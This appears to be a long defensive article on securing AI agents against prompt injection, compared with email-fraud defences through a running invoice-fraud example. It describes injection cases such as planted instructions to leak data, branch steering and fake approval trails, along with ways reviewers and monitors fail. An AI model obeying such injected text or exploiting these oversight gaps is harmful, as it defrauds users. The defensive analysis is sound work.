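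These figures show that attackers largely abandoned a method that had persisted despite years of warnings. They count campaigns rather than infected computers, so they don't measure how much harm the block prevented. Proofpoint's *Crime Finds a Way* credits the block with forcing criminal operations of every size to change how they work. But defenders had to close each new route separately, as they do when an agent can leak data through images, links and domain lookups.

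### Login keys that work only on the real site

Phishing training tells people to check a page's address before typing a password. Passkeys and hardware security keys make the check automatic.

1. When the clerk registers with a site, the clerk's device creates a pair of keys for that site's domain. It gives the site the public key and keeps the private one.
2. At each login, the site sends a random number. The browser passes it to the device along with the domain of the page the clerk is actually on.
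3. If the device has a key for that domain, it signs the number and the domain. Otherwise it does nothing.
4. The site checks the signature with the public key.

If the clerk lands on a perfect copy of the company's sign-in page at brightpaper-billing.example, the device finds no key for that domain. Even if the clerk is convinced the page is real, they have no secret to type in or read out over the phone. A six-digit code sent by text message gives much less protection, because a deceived clerk can type it into the fake page and the fraudster can then use it on the real one.

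Google told the journalist Brian Krebs in 2018 that none of its more than 85,000 employees had lost a work account to phishing since early 2017, when it began requiring security keys. Google was reporting on itself and there was no comparison group, but the record is striking for a company that size. Attackers can still target password resets and other fallback methods, or steal a session after the clerk has logged in. The keys don't stop invoice fraud either, because the clerk logs in to the company's real bank and then pays the wrong account.

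### Lowering an agent's privileges as it reads

The simplest equivalent for agents is a rule that when a model processes text from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's. The rule comes from an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, and David C recommends it to designers. A company wouldn't let an outsider use its payment system, so a model reading an outsider's email shouldn't be able to use the payment system either.

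Under this rule, the accounts assistant would start the morning with the clerk's privileges. As soon as it opened the supplier's email, software would take away the payment tool. The assistant could still do what the company lets any supplier do, such as submit an invoice for approval. If it then read a second supplier's email, it should keep only the privileges that both suppliers have, since either email might be influencing it. The assistant could regain the payment tool only in a fresh context that contained neither email.

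Applied literally, the rule would prevent most office work. A stranger can't read the clerk's inbox, so an assistant that had read one stranger's email couldn't open the next. In practice, a company would have to choose which privileges are dangerous enough to remove. The rule also depends on knowing who wrote the text, so a fraudster who had broken into a colleague's mailbox would get the colleague's privileges.

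Many agents instead log in as their user and keep all of that user's access. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) warns that a valid credential may let an agent into a system without establishing what it is authorised to do there.

### Three dangerous ingredients

In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) names three things that together let an attacker steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. A deceived assistant can't leak private data to a stranger if it can read the whole mailbox but has no way to send anything, or if it can send mail but has seen nothing private.

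Willison lists more than a dozen products with this weakness, from ChatGPT in April 2023 to Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2025. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route by which stolen data could leave. But a vendor can't protect users who connect several tools themselves. One tool may read private files, another may fetch strangers' web pages and a third may send messages. A single tool can also combine these abilities. GitHub's official connector for agents could read public bug reports that anyone might have written, open private code and publish changes.

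The three ingredients describe theft, but the fraudster in the running example wants a payment. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) covers both by broadening the third ingredient to include any action that changes something. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of these properties:

- A: it processes untrusted input.
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change something or communicate externally.

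The accounts assistant reads suppliers' emails, has access to the payment system and can make payments. The company could remove any one of these three abilities.

| Property removed | How the assistant would work | What the fraudster could still do |
|---|---|---|
| A | It reads mail only from verified suppliers | Write from a supplier's hacked mailbox |
| B | It reads each invoice without access to the mailbox or payment system, and adds it to a queue | Get a false invoice into the queue |
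| C | It prepares payments but can't make them | Deceive the clerk who approves them |

Meta allows an agent to change properties partway through a task if the change breaks the attack chain. For example, an agent could research suppliers on the web with no access to company data, then permanently lose its ability to communicate before opening internal files. Any hostile text it had read on the web would still be in its context, but the agent could no longer send anything to the attacker.

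Meta says an agent shouldn't work without supervision if its task needs all three properties in one session. It also says the rule doesn't prevent less severe results of prompt injection, such as false information in the agent's reply.

### A model that reads and a model that acts

A company can also divide the properties between two models. In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed a privileged model that takes the user's requests and has tools, and a quarantined model that reads untrusted text and has no tools. Ordinary software called the controller passes material between them.

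When the clerk asks for a summary of the supplier's email, the controller fetches the email and stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged model receives only that name, and calls the quarantined model to summarise `$VAR1`. The controller stores the summary as `$VAR2` and, on the privileged model's instruction, shows it to the clerk. The fraudster's words never reach the model that can act. The privileged model can receive an answer from the quarantined model only if code can check it completely, such as a choice between "invoice" and "not an invoice".

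Willison called the solution "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake could let hostile text reach the privileged model.

*Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw* (Cheng and Tsao, 2026) tested a looser version that is easier to build. One agent read the email and wrote a summary, and a second agent, which could send mail, read only that summary. In some tests, the first agent had to write in a fixed format called JSON, with fields for the sender, subject, summary and action items.

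The attacks came from a public contest that collected 461,640 attempts to make an email assistant send unauthorised messages. Cheng and Tsao tested a single agent using GPT-5-mini against the 22,899 different emails that had worked in the contest's first phase. Of these, 649 (2.83%) worked on this agent, and Cheng and Tsao used them to compare the defences.

| Set-up | Successful attacks out of 649 | Success rate |
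|---|---|---|
| One agent, structured summary | 92 | 14.18% |
| Two agents, ordinary text | 2 | 0.31% |
| Two agents, structured summary | 0 | 0% |

Splitting the agent in two helped far more than changing the format. The email could still cause a single agent to send a message, whatever format its summary took. After the split, the platform gave the reading agent no tool for sending mail, so it couldn't send anything even when the email had deceived it.

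The comparison probably makes all three set-ups look better than they are. Cheng and Tsao chose emails that had already worked once, and a model may resist the same email on a second try, so some of the attacks might have failed without any defence. The emails were also written to attack a single agent, and nobody adapted them to get past two.

That matters because the acting agent still read text that the attacker could influence. With both defences in place, 63.7% of the summaries contained material from the injection. This material had lost enough of its persuasive context to be harmless in these tests, but an attacker who knew about the summary could tailor the injection to the acting agent. The invoice fraudster hardly needs to, because "Bright Paper has a new bank account" is a fair summary of the email, and an acting agent that reads it may pay the new account.

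### Fixing the agent's actions before it reads

If an agent chooses its actions before it reads any untrusted text, an injection can't add new ones. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six designs that use this idea or a related one. The table applies them to the clerk's invoices.

| Design | How it works | What a hostile email can still do |
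|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model turns the clerk's request into one of a few fixed commands and never sees the results | Nothing to the model, but the model can't read invoices either |
| Plan, then execute | The model lists its tool calls before it opens any mail | Change the details of a listed call, such as the account number |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each file and answers only whether it is an invoice | Get its own file counted as an invoice |
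| Dual LLM | The acting model handles text by name, without seeing it | Change what the named text contains |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a whole program before any mail arrives | Change the data that the program handles |
| Context minimisation | Software removes the user's request before the model writes its reply | Almost anything, because this design guards against hostile requests from users |

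Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think fixing the actions in advance would make an email assistant only slightly less useful, since a stranger's email should rarely determine which actions it takes or in what order. Fixing the actions gives less protection to their content. If the clerk asks the assistant to send today's schedule to a manager, a hostile calendar entry can't add a second recipient to the plan, but it can change the message.

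### CaMeL and the morning's invoices

CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind published in 2025, combines the last type of plan, a program, with labels that follow each piece of data. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that CaMeL fixes a flaw in the dual-model design. A user might ask an assistant to send Bob a document at the address in the meeting notes. The quarantined model has to find the address, so an attacker who can edit the notes can substitute their own and receive the document without changing the plan.

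Here is how CaMeL could handle the clerk's invoices.

1. The clerk asks the assistant to pay this morning's invoices. A planning model receives the request and a description of each tool, but no email.
2. The planning model writes a program in a restricted form of Python. In simplified form, it might look like this:

```
for email in get_unread_mail():
    invoice = ask_reader("Find the amount and account number", email)
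    pay(account=invoice.account, amount=invoice.amount)
```

3. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program. It fetches the emails and labels each one with its source.
4. For each email, the interpreter calls a second model, the reader, which has no tools and must answer in a set format. The fraudster's email can make the reader give a false answer, but it can't add a line to the program.
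5. The interpreter labels the account number as coming from that email. Any value that the program calculates from the number gets the same label.
6. Before each payment, a policy written in ordinary code checks the labels. If the company accepts account numbers only from the clerk or its own payment records, the interpreter blocks the payment or asks the clerk.

The October attack would fail at step 4 because it relied on the assistant forwarding an email, and this program contains no instruction to forward anything.

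The invoice fraud gets as far as step 6 because the program is written to pay an account number from an email. Without a policy on account numbers, CaMeL would follow its plan and pay the fraudster. The company therefore has to know in advance which values need a policy. Willison worries about this burden, because someone has to write the policies and keep them up to date, which even experienced security people find difficult.

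A better plan would take only the supplier's name from the email and look up the account number in the payment records. The fraudster could then make the assistant pay Bright Paper too much or too early, but the money would go to Bright Paper.

### Checking the plan in advance

CaMeL applies its policies as the program runs, so the assistant may work through half the invoices before it discovers that the plan breaks a rule. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, add a check before the program starts. Their software turns the program into a map of every path it could take, and a tool called a model checker looks for a path that breaks a rule. If it finds one, it describes the path to the planning model, which tries to repair the program. One of their rules covers payments:

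AG(send_money → ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted))

AG means "at every step of every path". Under this rule, whenever the program sends money, neither the recipient nor the amount may come from an untrusted source. An accounts department couldn't use the rule unchanged, because the amount on an invoice always comes from the supplier. It could replace the condition on the amount with a spending limit and keep the condition on the recipient.

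CaMeLoT can also check that something eventually happens. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a security team that requires every open incident to be closed. A company could similarly require the assistant to report every invoice it doesn't pay, so that a blocked payment doesn't go unnoticed. The check can't determine how many times a loop will run, so it may reject some safe plans that contain loops.

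### What false data can still change

In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) use labels of this kind in a small formal language for describing agents. They prove that changing data labelled untrusted can't affect any value that the program recognises as trusted. The proof doesn't depend on how well the model resists deception, so it holds even when the reader makes mistakes.

In practice, the interpreter has to apply the labels without gaps. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) reports a flaw that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL's interpreter. A program might start by setting `approved` to true and change it to false if the reader finds something suspicious in the email. If the fraudster convinces the reader that nothing is wrong, the program skips the change, and `approved` may keep its trusted label even though the email determined its value.

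An attacker can also use false data to control which of the plan's existing actions the agent takes. A planning model might write a program that pays if the email says someone has verified the new bank details, and otherwise asks the clerk. The fraudster's email says someone has, so the program pays. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) call this branch steering in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*. They studied agents that control a computer by looking at its screen and clicking. In one attack, an advertisement imitated a cookie notice. The plan included a routine step to find and close cookie notices, so the agent clicked the advertisement and went to the attacker's site.

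Policies are harder to write for agents that work by clicking on a screen. A rule can forbid payments to unknown accounts, but a click at a certain point on the screen might log in, delete a file or pay someone, depending on what is there. Foerster and colleagues tried comparing the screen with the page's underlying code and consulting a second model, but an attacker can try to manipulate those checks too.

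None of these designs prevents false summaries. CaMeL would pass one on to the clerk, because displaying the summary is part of the plan.

### What the separation costs

CaMeL's developers reported that it completed 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo, compared with 84% for an agent without it. Peters-Gill and colleagues later found a larger loss on industrial maintenance tasks, which they tested with a coordinating agent and four specialist agents. Across five models, CaMeL lowered the share of completed tasks by an average of 21.6 percentage points. The loss was 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, so it may shrink further as models improve.

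Most of the failures happened because the planning model had to write its program before seeing any data. An ordinary agent that finds "see attached credit note" in an invoice can decide to open the credit note, but a CaMeL agent can open it only if its program allowed for that possibility. Also, when a specialist couldn't find records for the requested dates, it sometimes returned records for other dates, and the coordinator's program used them without detecting the mismatch.

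Planning ahead is even harder when the agent works from a screen. Foerster and colleagues' plans averaged 213 lines of code and about 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and four branches for tasks in AgentDojo. About half of each plan was fallback code that didn't run. The agents performed at most 57% as well as the strongest models usually do.

When a task suits the design, the agent can lose little usefulness. *The Framing Gap* tested a simple planner and reader on a small model, Llama-3.1-8B, that had to summarise web pages without leaking a secret. None of 210 attacks succeeded, and nine of ten summaries of harmless pages still named the main people and things. This was an easy case because the planner could plan a summary without knowing what was on the page.

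### When one protected agent instructs another

Companies increasingly use several agents together, and protecting each one separately may not be enough. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents, in which a coordinator could ask one agent to search a database and another to send messages. They asked the system to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack, and planted an instruction in the database to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

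The first two agents followed their plans. The coordinator then included the summary, with its planted instruction, in its request to the messaging agent. That agent treated the whole request, including the untrusted summary, as coming from its user, so its planning model read the instruction and added a step to email the attacker.

The remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into an instruction, which can't include anything that came from a tool, and data, which the receiving agent's planning model never sees. On a version of AgentDojo adapted for several agents, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with each agent protected separately and never with multi-CaMeL. The test used a fixed set of attacks, and GPT-5.5 resisted all of them without any protection, so the result is weak evidence about how multi-CaMeL would fare against attackers who adapt. The extra protection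 lowered task completion on the maintenance tasks by 3.2 points.

### Whether useful agents need all three ingredients

Bowley argues in *Does the "lethal trifecta" kill the idea of fully autonomous AI Agents* that people don't yet appreciate how much the three ingredients restrict what agents can do. Customers' emails, suppliers' documents and web pages are all untrusted, and most office jobs combine them with private records and some way to reply. An assistant that lacks any one of the three might be safe but not worth buying.

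Companies are selling agents with broad access. Willison files posts about OpenAI's ChatGPT Work, announced in July 2026, under the tag "lethal-trifecta". He uses the same tag for Anthropic's decision to make auto mode, in which its coding agent asks for approval less often, the default for most of its paid plans. The clearest evidence of limits in real products is still for the simplest limit, closing the routes by which data can leave, while the results for CaMeL and its successors come from benchmarks.

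Beurer-Kellner and colleagues argue that companies should stop expecting one agent to do everything. An agent that only sorts invoices needs far less access than a general assistant, and its designers can work out what a hostile invoice could make it do. They doubt that general-purpose agents built on current language models can offer reliable safety guarantees.

CaMeL instead lets a system have all three ingredients as long as no single model has them all. The planning model has tools but receives no untrusted text. The reader model processes that text without access to tools, and ordinary code controls what passes between the two. This works well for the accounts assistant because the company can specify exactly where an account number may come from.

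Other tasks are harder to divide. Meta admits that some popular uses fit its rule badly, such as background jobs where stopping for a person's approval would be disruptive or ineffective. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe another difficult case, in which a user tells an assistant to reply to an email with the information the sender wants. The sender chooses what to ask for, and the assistant has to find the answer in the user's private mail and send it back. A policy against giving private data to outsiders would stop a thief, but it would also stop the assistant from doing what the user asked. The company could restrict the search to earlier correspondence with the same sender. Someone would then have to decide whether the sender should have anything more.

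## Checking requests with people and independent records

An accounts assistant's job is to get suppliers paid, so a company can't take away everything that makes it dangerous. But the company can check each payment before the money leaves, either by asking a person to approve it or by having code compare it with a record that the email's author can't change. Companies use both methods against business email compromise, which gives a mail system very little to detect.

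### A plausible request in plain text

Filters miss the fraudster's email about a new bank account because an honest supplier could have written the same sentence, and sandboxes miss it because it contains no code to run.

Victims reported losing $3.05 billion to business email compromise in 2025, up from $2.77 billion in 2024, according to the FBI's *2025 IC3 Annual Report* (2026). Only investment fraud cost more. The average loss across the 24,768 complaints was about $123,000, compared with about $1,100 for complaints the FBI classed as phishing or spoofing. Actual losses are probably higher, since some victims never report them.

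Injection classifiers have the same difficulty with emails to agents. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) describes a test on 8,400 professional-sounding emails, some of which claimed an authority the user had never granted. Each email had two versions, which differed by a single clause. Meta's classifier Prompt Guard 2 scored 0.59 at telling the versions apart, where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. To do better, it would have needed information about what the user had authorised.

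### Call-backs and second approvers

The FBI's *Business Email Compromise Contributes To Large Scale Business Losses Nationwide* advises companies to phone the person who made a request before paying. J.P. Morgan adds that the number should come from a company directory and never from the email.

If the clerk looks up Bright Paper's number and calls to ask about the new account, the supplier will say that it hasn't changed banks. This works however convincing the email was, because the clerk doesn't have to judge the message and the fraudster doesn't answer Bright Paper's phone.

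A fraudster might email a company a new phone number in March and a new bank account in April, so that a call to verify the account reaches the fraudster. The FBI therefore tells companies to verify changes to contact information as well as bank details.

The FBI also suggests having two people sign off on transfers. A second approver helps only if they check something for themselves. A manager who approves the payment after reading the forwarded email has seen the same false message as the clerk, now with the clerk's endorsement. The manager would do better to phone to confirm the request or look up past payments. *Best Practices for Businesses to Detect the BEC Scam* (2023), a bank's checklist, suggests asking whether the account differs from the one used before, and whether a supplier who used to accept cheques now wants a wire transfer.

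J.P. Morgan warns that call-backs can fail without formal procedures. A clerk has little reason to call if they believe the email, especially if the invoice is due today. The payment program can enforce call-backs by refusing new bank details until a second employee has recorded a call, although someone in a hurry could record a call they never made.

### Training staff to be alert

Companies also train their staff to spot fraudulent emails, but two large trials suggest that this achieves little.

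In *Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice*, Ho, Mirian and colleagues (2025) analysed an eight-month trial with more than 19,500 employees at UC San Diego Health. The hospital system sent simulated phishing emails about once a month. People who clicked a link saw either training material or, in the control group, an ordinary error page. The training came in four forms, some interactive and some tailored to the email that had fooled the employee.

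Phishing training reduced the average failure rate by only about 2%. Slashdot's *Phishing Training Is Pretty Pointless, Researchers Find* reports that the researchers gave the figure as 1.7% in their conference talk. Employees who had recently completed the annual security course did no better than those who had taken it long before.

The choice of email mattered far more. UC San Diego's *Cybersecurity Training Programs Don't Prevent Employees from Falling for Phishing Scams* reports that 1.82% of recipients clicked on a link to update their Outlook password, while 30.8% clicked on one about a supposed change to the vacation policy. More than half of the staff clicked on at least one link during the trial.

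Part of the problem was that few people studied the material. Over half of the training sessions ended within ten seconds. People who finished the interactive version were 19% less likely to click on a later email, but Ho and colleagues point out that they may have been more careful to begin with.

*Anti-Phishing Training (Still) Does Not Work* (Rozema and Davis, 2025) reports a similar result from a study of 12,511 employees at a financial technology company. One group watched lectures, another also did exercises, and a control group received no training until the study ended. Each person then received one simulated phishing email.

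| | Trained | Untrained |
|---|---|---|
| Clicked on the link | 10.5% | 9.8% |
| Reported the email | 9.7% | 8.9% |

Neither difference was statistically significant. The control group had only 462 people, too few to rule out an improvement of one or two percentage points. Training may have helped with the most deceptive emails, but the evidence for this comes from even fewer untrained people.

Both trials measured clicks on links, so they don't directly show how staff respond to a false invoice. But an invoice email without a link gives staff even fewer warning signs. The researchers in San Diego recommend technical measures instead, such as password managers that work only on the correct domain. For a change of bank details, the nearest equivalent is a payment program that blocks the new account until it has been verified.

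### Confirmation prompts

The usual human check on an agent is a confirmation prompt, where software pauses a tool call and asks the user to allow or deny it. The pause has to come from code, because an agent can ignore an instruction to ask first. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, recounts how a safety researcher told an agent to "confirm before acting". The agent began deleting messages from the researcher's inbox anyway, and didn't stop when told to.

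Products differ in when they ask the user for approval. In manual mode, Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, asks before it runs commands or changes files. Yan instead sorts actions by their consequences and lets the user set a rule for each of four kinds: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something, and reading private data.

Narrow rules can keep requests for a person's approval rare. In *LivePI*, Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban (2026) used fixed rules to allow each tool call, block it or hold it for a person to review, based on factors such as the tool, its arguments and any warnings from a detector. In ordinary work, the rules held 8 of 899 calls and blocked one. Together with a filter on incoming text, the rules reduced the success rate of 169 test attacks on one model from 27.2% to zero.

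Zhao and colleagues wrote some of the rules with these attacks in mind. They also counted an attack as stopped once the software held it for review, so the zero depends on the reviewer saying no. Some of their test attacks included a fabricated trail of approvals, or a claim that someone had already approved the action and the agent should resume without asking again. A reviewer who saw these claims might well believe them.

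Letting an agent explain its own request is dangerous because the explanation may repeat an attacker's claims. Suppose a fraudster's email deceives the accounts assistant, which then sends the clerk the message, "Pay Bright Paper's invoice for $8,000? The new bank details have been verified." The second sentence is the fraudster's claim in the assistant's words. If the clerk relies on it, they approve the payment without an independent check of the bank details.

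Showing the raw command doesn't always help either. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), a review of 290 incident reports, found 31 that involved prompts showing a command but not its effect. A request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code the script contains.

### Approval fatigue

People who see many prompts tend to stop reading them. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts. That figure alone is weak evidence that users aren't reading the prompts, since most of the commands are presumably harmless. But users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents for approval, so they seem willing to refuse larger requests.

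Anthropic also had an outside firm run an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, the text of one prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

The testers weren't working on their own projects and had less to lose than real users. Anthropic also used the result to justify asking users less often. Even so, neither fact easily explains a fall to 5% in a test where the command was meant to be obvious.

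*Looks Fine to Me* (2026), based on interviews with 12 people about their everyday use of AI, concludes that users often don't notice when their oversight lapses. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approvals may reflect fatigue or deadlines instead of growing trust. A product that treats these approvals as a preference and stops asking may be learning from careless clicks. In the review of incident reports, 80 cases involved users who had turned on automatic approval, often to avoid hundreds of prompts in a session.

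Fatigue only partly explains why people approve actions that go beyond the task. Yan had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the task. Participants who had to approve or reject every action still allowed 40% of those seven.

Another group first set rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for the four kinds of action. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and approved 67% of the out-of-task actions that the software asked them about. They saw fewer prompts than the first group, but let more out-of-task actions through overall.

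No attacker took part in Yan's experiment, and some of the extra actions were arguably helpful, such as calling the airport to confirm a flight, so not every approval should be counted as a mistake. But about half of the people with "ask" rules who saw a request to announce publicly that they were travelling agreed to it, compared with a fifth of those who had to approve each action individually.

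### Replacing the reviewer with a model

In Anthropic's alternative, called auto mode, a second model reviews the actions. It blocked 89% of the dangerous commands used in the experiment with testers, and its performance didn't decline over a long session.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains how the design limits a deceived agent's influence on the model that reviews its actions. The reviewer receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, while software removes the agent's explanations and everything its tools returned. An injection can still deceive the agent, but neither the injection nor the agent's account of it reaches the reviewer.

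In an earlier test, the system missed 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone too far. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

Like AgentWatcher, this reviewer would probably let the fraudulent payment through, because paying Bright Paper fits the clerk's request. Hiding the email keeps the reviewer from being misled by it, but doesn't provide the information needed to detect the fraud.

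### What a useful prompt shows

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) tests how much better people judge requests when they have better evidence. In one example, a user asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send the auditor only the totals. A note from a vendor contains an injection, and the agent copies the full invoice rows into report.csv. It then asks permission to send report.csv to the auditor. The recipient and the tool are both permitted, so nothing in the request looks wrong.

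The researchers had 80 volunteers make 960 decisions, half of them about unsafe requests. Each person used one of four displays.

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| Exact details of the tool call | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Those details, the user's original instructions and a log of every step | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
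| The same facts, with a sentence stating the combined effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

In the invoice case, the last display showed that the agent had built the attachment from raw invoice rows and was about to send it to the auditor. Most of the improvement came from showing the facts at all, and that display's advantage over the log could be due to chance.

A separate recorder took those facts from the agent's actual tool calls, not its own account of them. If the agent changed the recipient after the user approved, the software would check the action again. An approval should cover one exact action, or a deceived agent could get permission for a harmless payment and then make a different one.

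Even with the best display, people approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests. Half of the requests were unsafe, so people were expecting trouble, and a clerk who approves honest payments all year would probably do worse.

### Comparing the payment with the supplier file

A person often doesn't need to look at the evidence, because code can compare two facts. The company could check the assistant's payment this way.

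1. The assistant proposes to pay Bright Paper $8,000, into an account ending in 7730.
2. The payment software looks up Bright Paper in the supplier file and finds an account ending in 2291.
3. The numbers differ, so the software holds the payment. It shows an employee both account numbers and the supplier's phone number on file, and leaves out the assistant's explanation.
4. The employee calls Bright Paper. If the supplier confirms the change, a second employee updates the file and releases the payment. Otherwise, the payment stays blocked.

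The comparison gives the same result even if the email has completely deceived the assistant, and the call gives the employee a source other than the email. Wu and colleagues used the same principle when they checked claims about a mailbox against the mail provider's records. This approach works only when someone keeps a record that contains the answer.

The record also has to be independent. If the assistant can edit the supplier file, a fraudster can get it to change the account number before paying, and the two numbers will match. If a clerk once copied an account number from a fraudulent email, payments to that account will keep passing the check. A new supplier has no record to check against, so its first payment needs a phone call.

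An account check doesn't catch a wrong amount or a duplicate invoice, though code could compare those with purchase orders and past payments.

A case in the FBI's annual report shows how a record and a confirmation can together help reverse a fraud. In April 2025, a fraudulent email led a city government office in Oregon to send more than $6 million to an account that the receiving bank had frozen the month before, after a fraud in Missouri. The receiving bank asked the city's bank whether the payment instructions were valid, and the city's bank was able to recall the transfer. The city was lucky that the criminals had reused an account, but the email that fooled the people who sent the money did not affect the receiving bank's record.

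### Choosing between a person and a record

If a reliable record contains the answer, code should check the request against it. People are more useful when no record exists or the record disagrees with the request. Hossain and colleagues similarly suggest that software should decide the clear cases and send the uncertain ones to a person, noting what evidence is missing.

A strong reason to prefer code is that it interrupts people less often. As an invented example, suppose the assistant pays 40 invoices on each of 250 working days, and the company has 400 suppliers, 5% of whom change banks in a year. A prompt for every payment would interrupt the clerk 10,000 times a year. Apart from any frauds and new suppliers, the comparison would interrupt someone about 20 times a year, for honest changes of bank, and a person can make a careful phone call that often.

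A longer delay is more worthwhile when an action is hard to undo. *A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) recommends sorting actions by whether someone can undo them and how much damage they could do. Software then blocks the forbidden actions, allows the low-risk ones and asks a person about the rest. *Let the Agent Do It?* suggests that confirmation prompts should also show whether an action is reversible, with stronger warnings or a second confirmation if it isn't.

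Finally, the person approving a request has to be able to see the raw facts. Someone who sees only the agent's summary has no basis for disagreeing with it, so a company shouldn't count their approval as a safeguard. For the accounts assistant, these rules might lead to the following choices.

| Action | Can the company undo it? | How often? | Suitable check |
|---|---|---|---|
| File an invoice in a folder | Yes | Constantly | None beforehand, but keep a log |
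| Pay an account on file | Often not | Daily | Code compares the account and enforces a spending limit |
| Pay a new or changed account | Often not | Rarely | Code holds the payment and a person calls the supplier |
| Send private information to a new recipient | No | Occasionally | A person sees the full message, attachments and exact address |

The last row is the weakest because no record shows what the recipient should know. The person has to judge this themselves, and a convincing story may deceive them too.

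A check also has to cover every route to the same result. *Let the Agent Do It?* notes that agents look for another way after a user denies a request, so an assistant that can't use the payment tool might try the bank's website. The company should put the comparison in the payment system or with the bank, not only in the assistant's software. The comparison will then also stop a clerk who reads a false summary and tries to pay the fraudster by hand.

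## Finding and undoing an attack after delivery

Some hostile emails get past every check and reach a reader. Email defenders therefore plan to find each one quickly, remove any other copies and repair what damage they can. Companies can do the same after an email deceives an agent, but the damage is in different places.

### Reporting and removing an email

Suppose the clerk suspects the supplier's email and presses the report button. In Microsoft's system, this starts an automated investigation that examines the sender, searches other mailboxes for similar messages and checks whether anyone clicked a malicious link. The system then recommends actions such as deleting the copies, and by default the security team must approve them.

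Microsoft's *Automated remediation in Automated investigation and response (AIR)* explains how a company can skip that approval when messages share a malicious file or link. Groups of more than 10,000 messages still need a person's approval, since a wrong verdict could remove a harmless announcement from every mailbox. Staff can usually restore what the software deleted.

Removal can also start without a report. If Microsoft's filters identify a message as malicious after delivery, the zero-hour auto purge feature moves it to junk or quarantine. The purge covers the last 48 hours of mail and, for phishing and malware, includes messages people have already read. In the hospital study, the risk from a phishing email lasted about three days, so an email identified as phishing on the third day may still be a risk but is too old to purge.

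These tools work best against an email sent to many people. If the fraudster wrote only to the clerk, there are no other copies to find, and deleting the email doesn't bring the money back. It also doesn't remove anything an AI assistant has copied from the email into its notes. Microsoft doesn't notify users of a purge, so the company itself would have to connect the purge to the assistant's software.

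### The 15-month experiment

Lain, Kostiainen and Capkun tested a report button, warnings and training at a company with more than 56,000 employees in *Phishing in Organizations* (2022). Between July 2019 and October 2020, the company sent each of 14,733 employees eight simulated phishing emails. It randomly assigned the employees to groups that differed in the warnings they saw, the feedback they received on their reports, and whether failing a test led to a training page.

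The researchers counted clicks and "dangerous actions", which meant submitting a login or enabling macros in an attachment. By the end, 32% of participants had clicked at least once and 25% had taken a dangerous action. The table compares the warning groups (each about a third of participants), then the training groups (each about half).

| Group | Clicks | Dangerous actions |
|---|---|---|
| No warning | 3,964 | 2,994 |
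| Short warning | 1,427 | 998 |
| Detailed warning | 1,289 | 893 |
| No training page | 3,087 | 2,155 |
| Training page after a failed test | 3,593 | 2,730 |

The short warning cut dangerous actions by 67%. The detailed warning, which listed reasons for suspicion, was not significantly better. The company put warnings only on its simulated emails, so some staff may have learned that a warning meant a test.

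The group assigned to training took 27% more dangerous actions than the group without it. The training page explained the clues in the email and offered a video and quizzes, which were optional. In a later questionnaire, 43% of those who remembered the page said it made them feel safe, and 40% said the company was protecting them from bad emails. The training may have given people a false sense of security, but this explanation is tentative because only 151 people completed the questionnaire. Lain (2024), in *Content, Nudges and Incentives*, later found that such training helps by reminding people of the threat, not through what it teaches.

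The report button worked better. Employees who used computers for varied office work reported 22% of the simulated emails, and reporting did not decline over the 15 months. About 10% of reports arrived within five minutes of delivery and 30% to 40% within half an hour.

Lain and colleagues estimate that if a campaign reached 100 employees, 8 to 25 of them would report it, and that at least one report would very probably arrive within five minutes. The five-minute estimate is a little optimistic, because if each report independently has a 10% chance of arriving that fast, the chance of at least one is 57% with eight reports and 93% with 25. The chance that at least one arrives within half an hour is 94% or higher, even with eight reports.

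Staff reports were correct about 68% of the time, or 79% counting reports of ordinary spam. About 21,000 people had the reporting button, but a second, stricter scanner sorted their reports and left the IT department only about 1.5 emails a day to examine by hand. In the last five months, staff reported 918 real phishing emails. The researchers searched for similar messages and found 252 large campaigns containing 28,830 emails.

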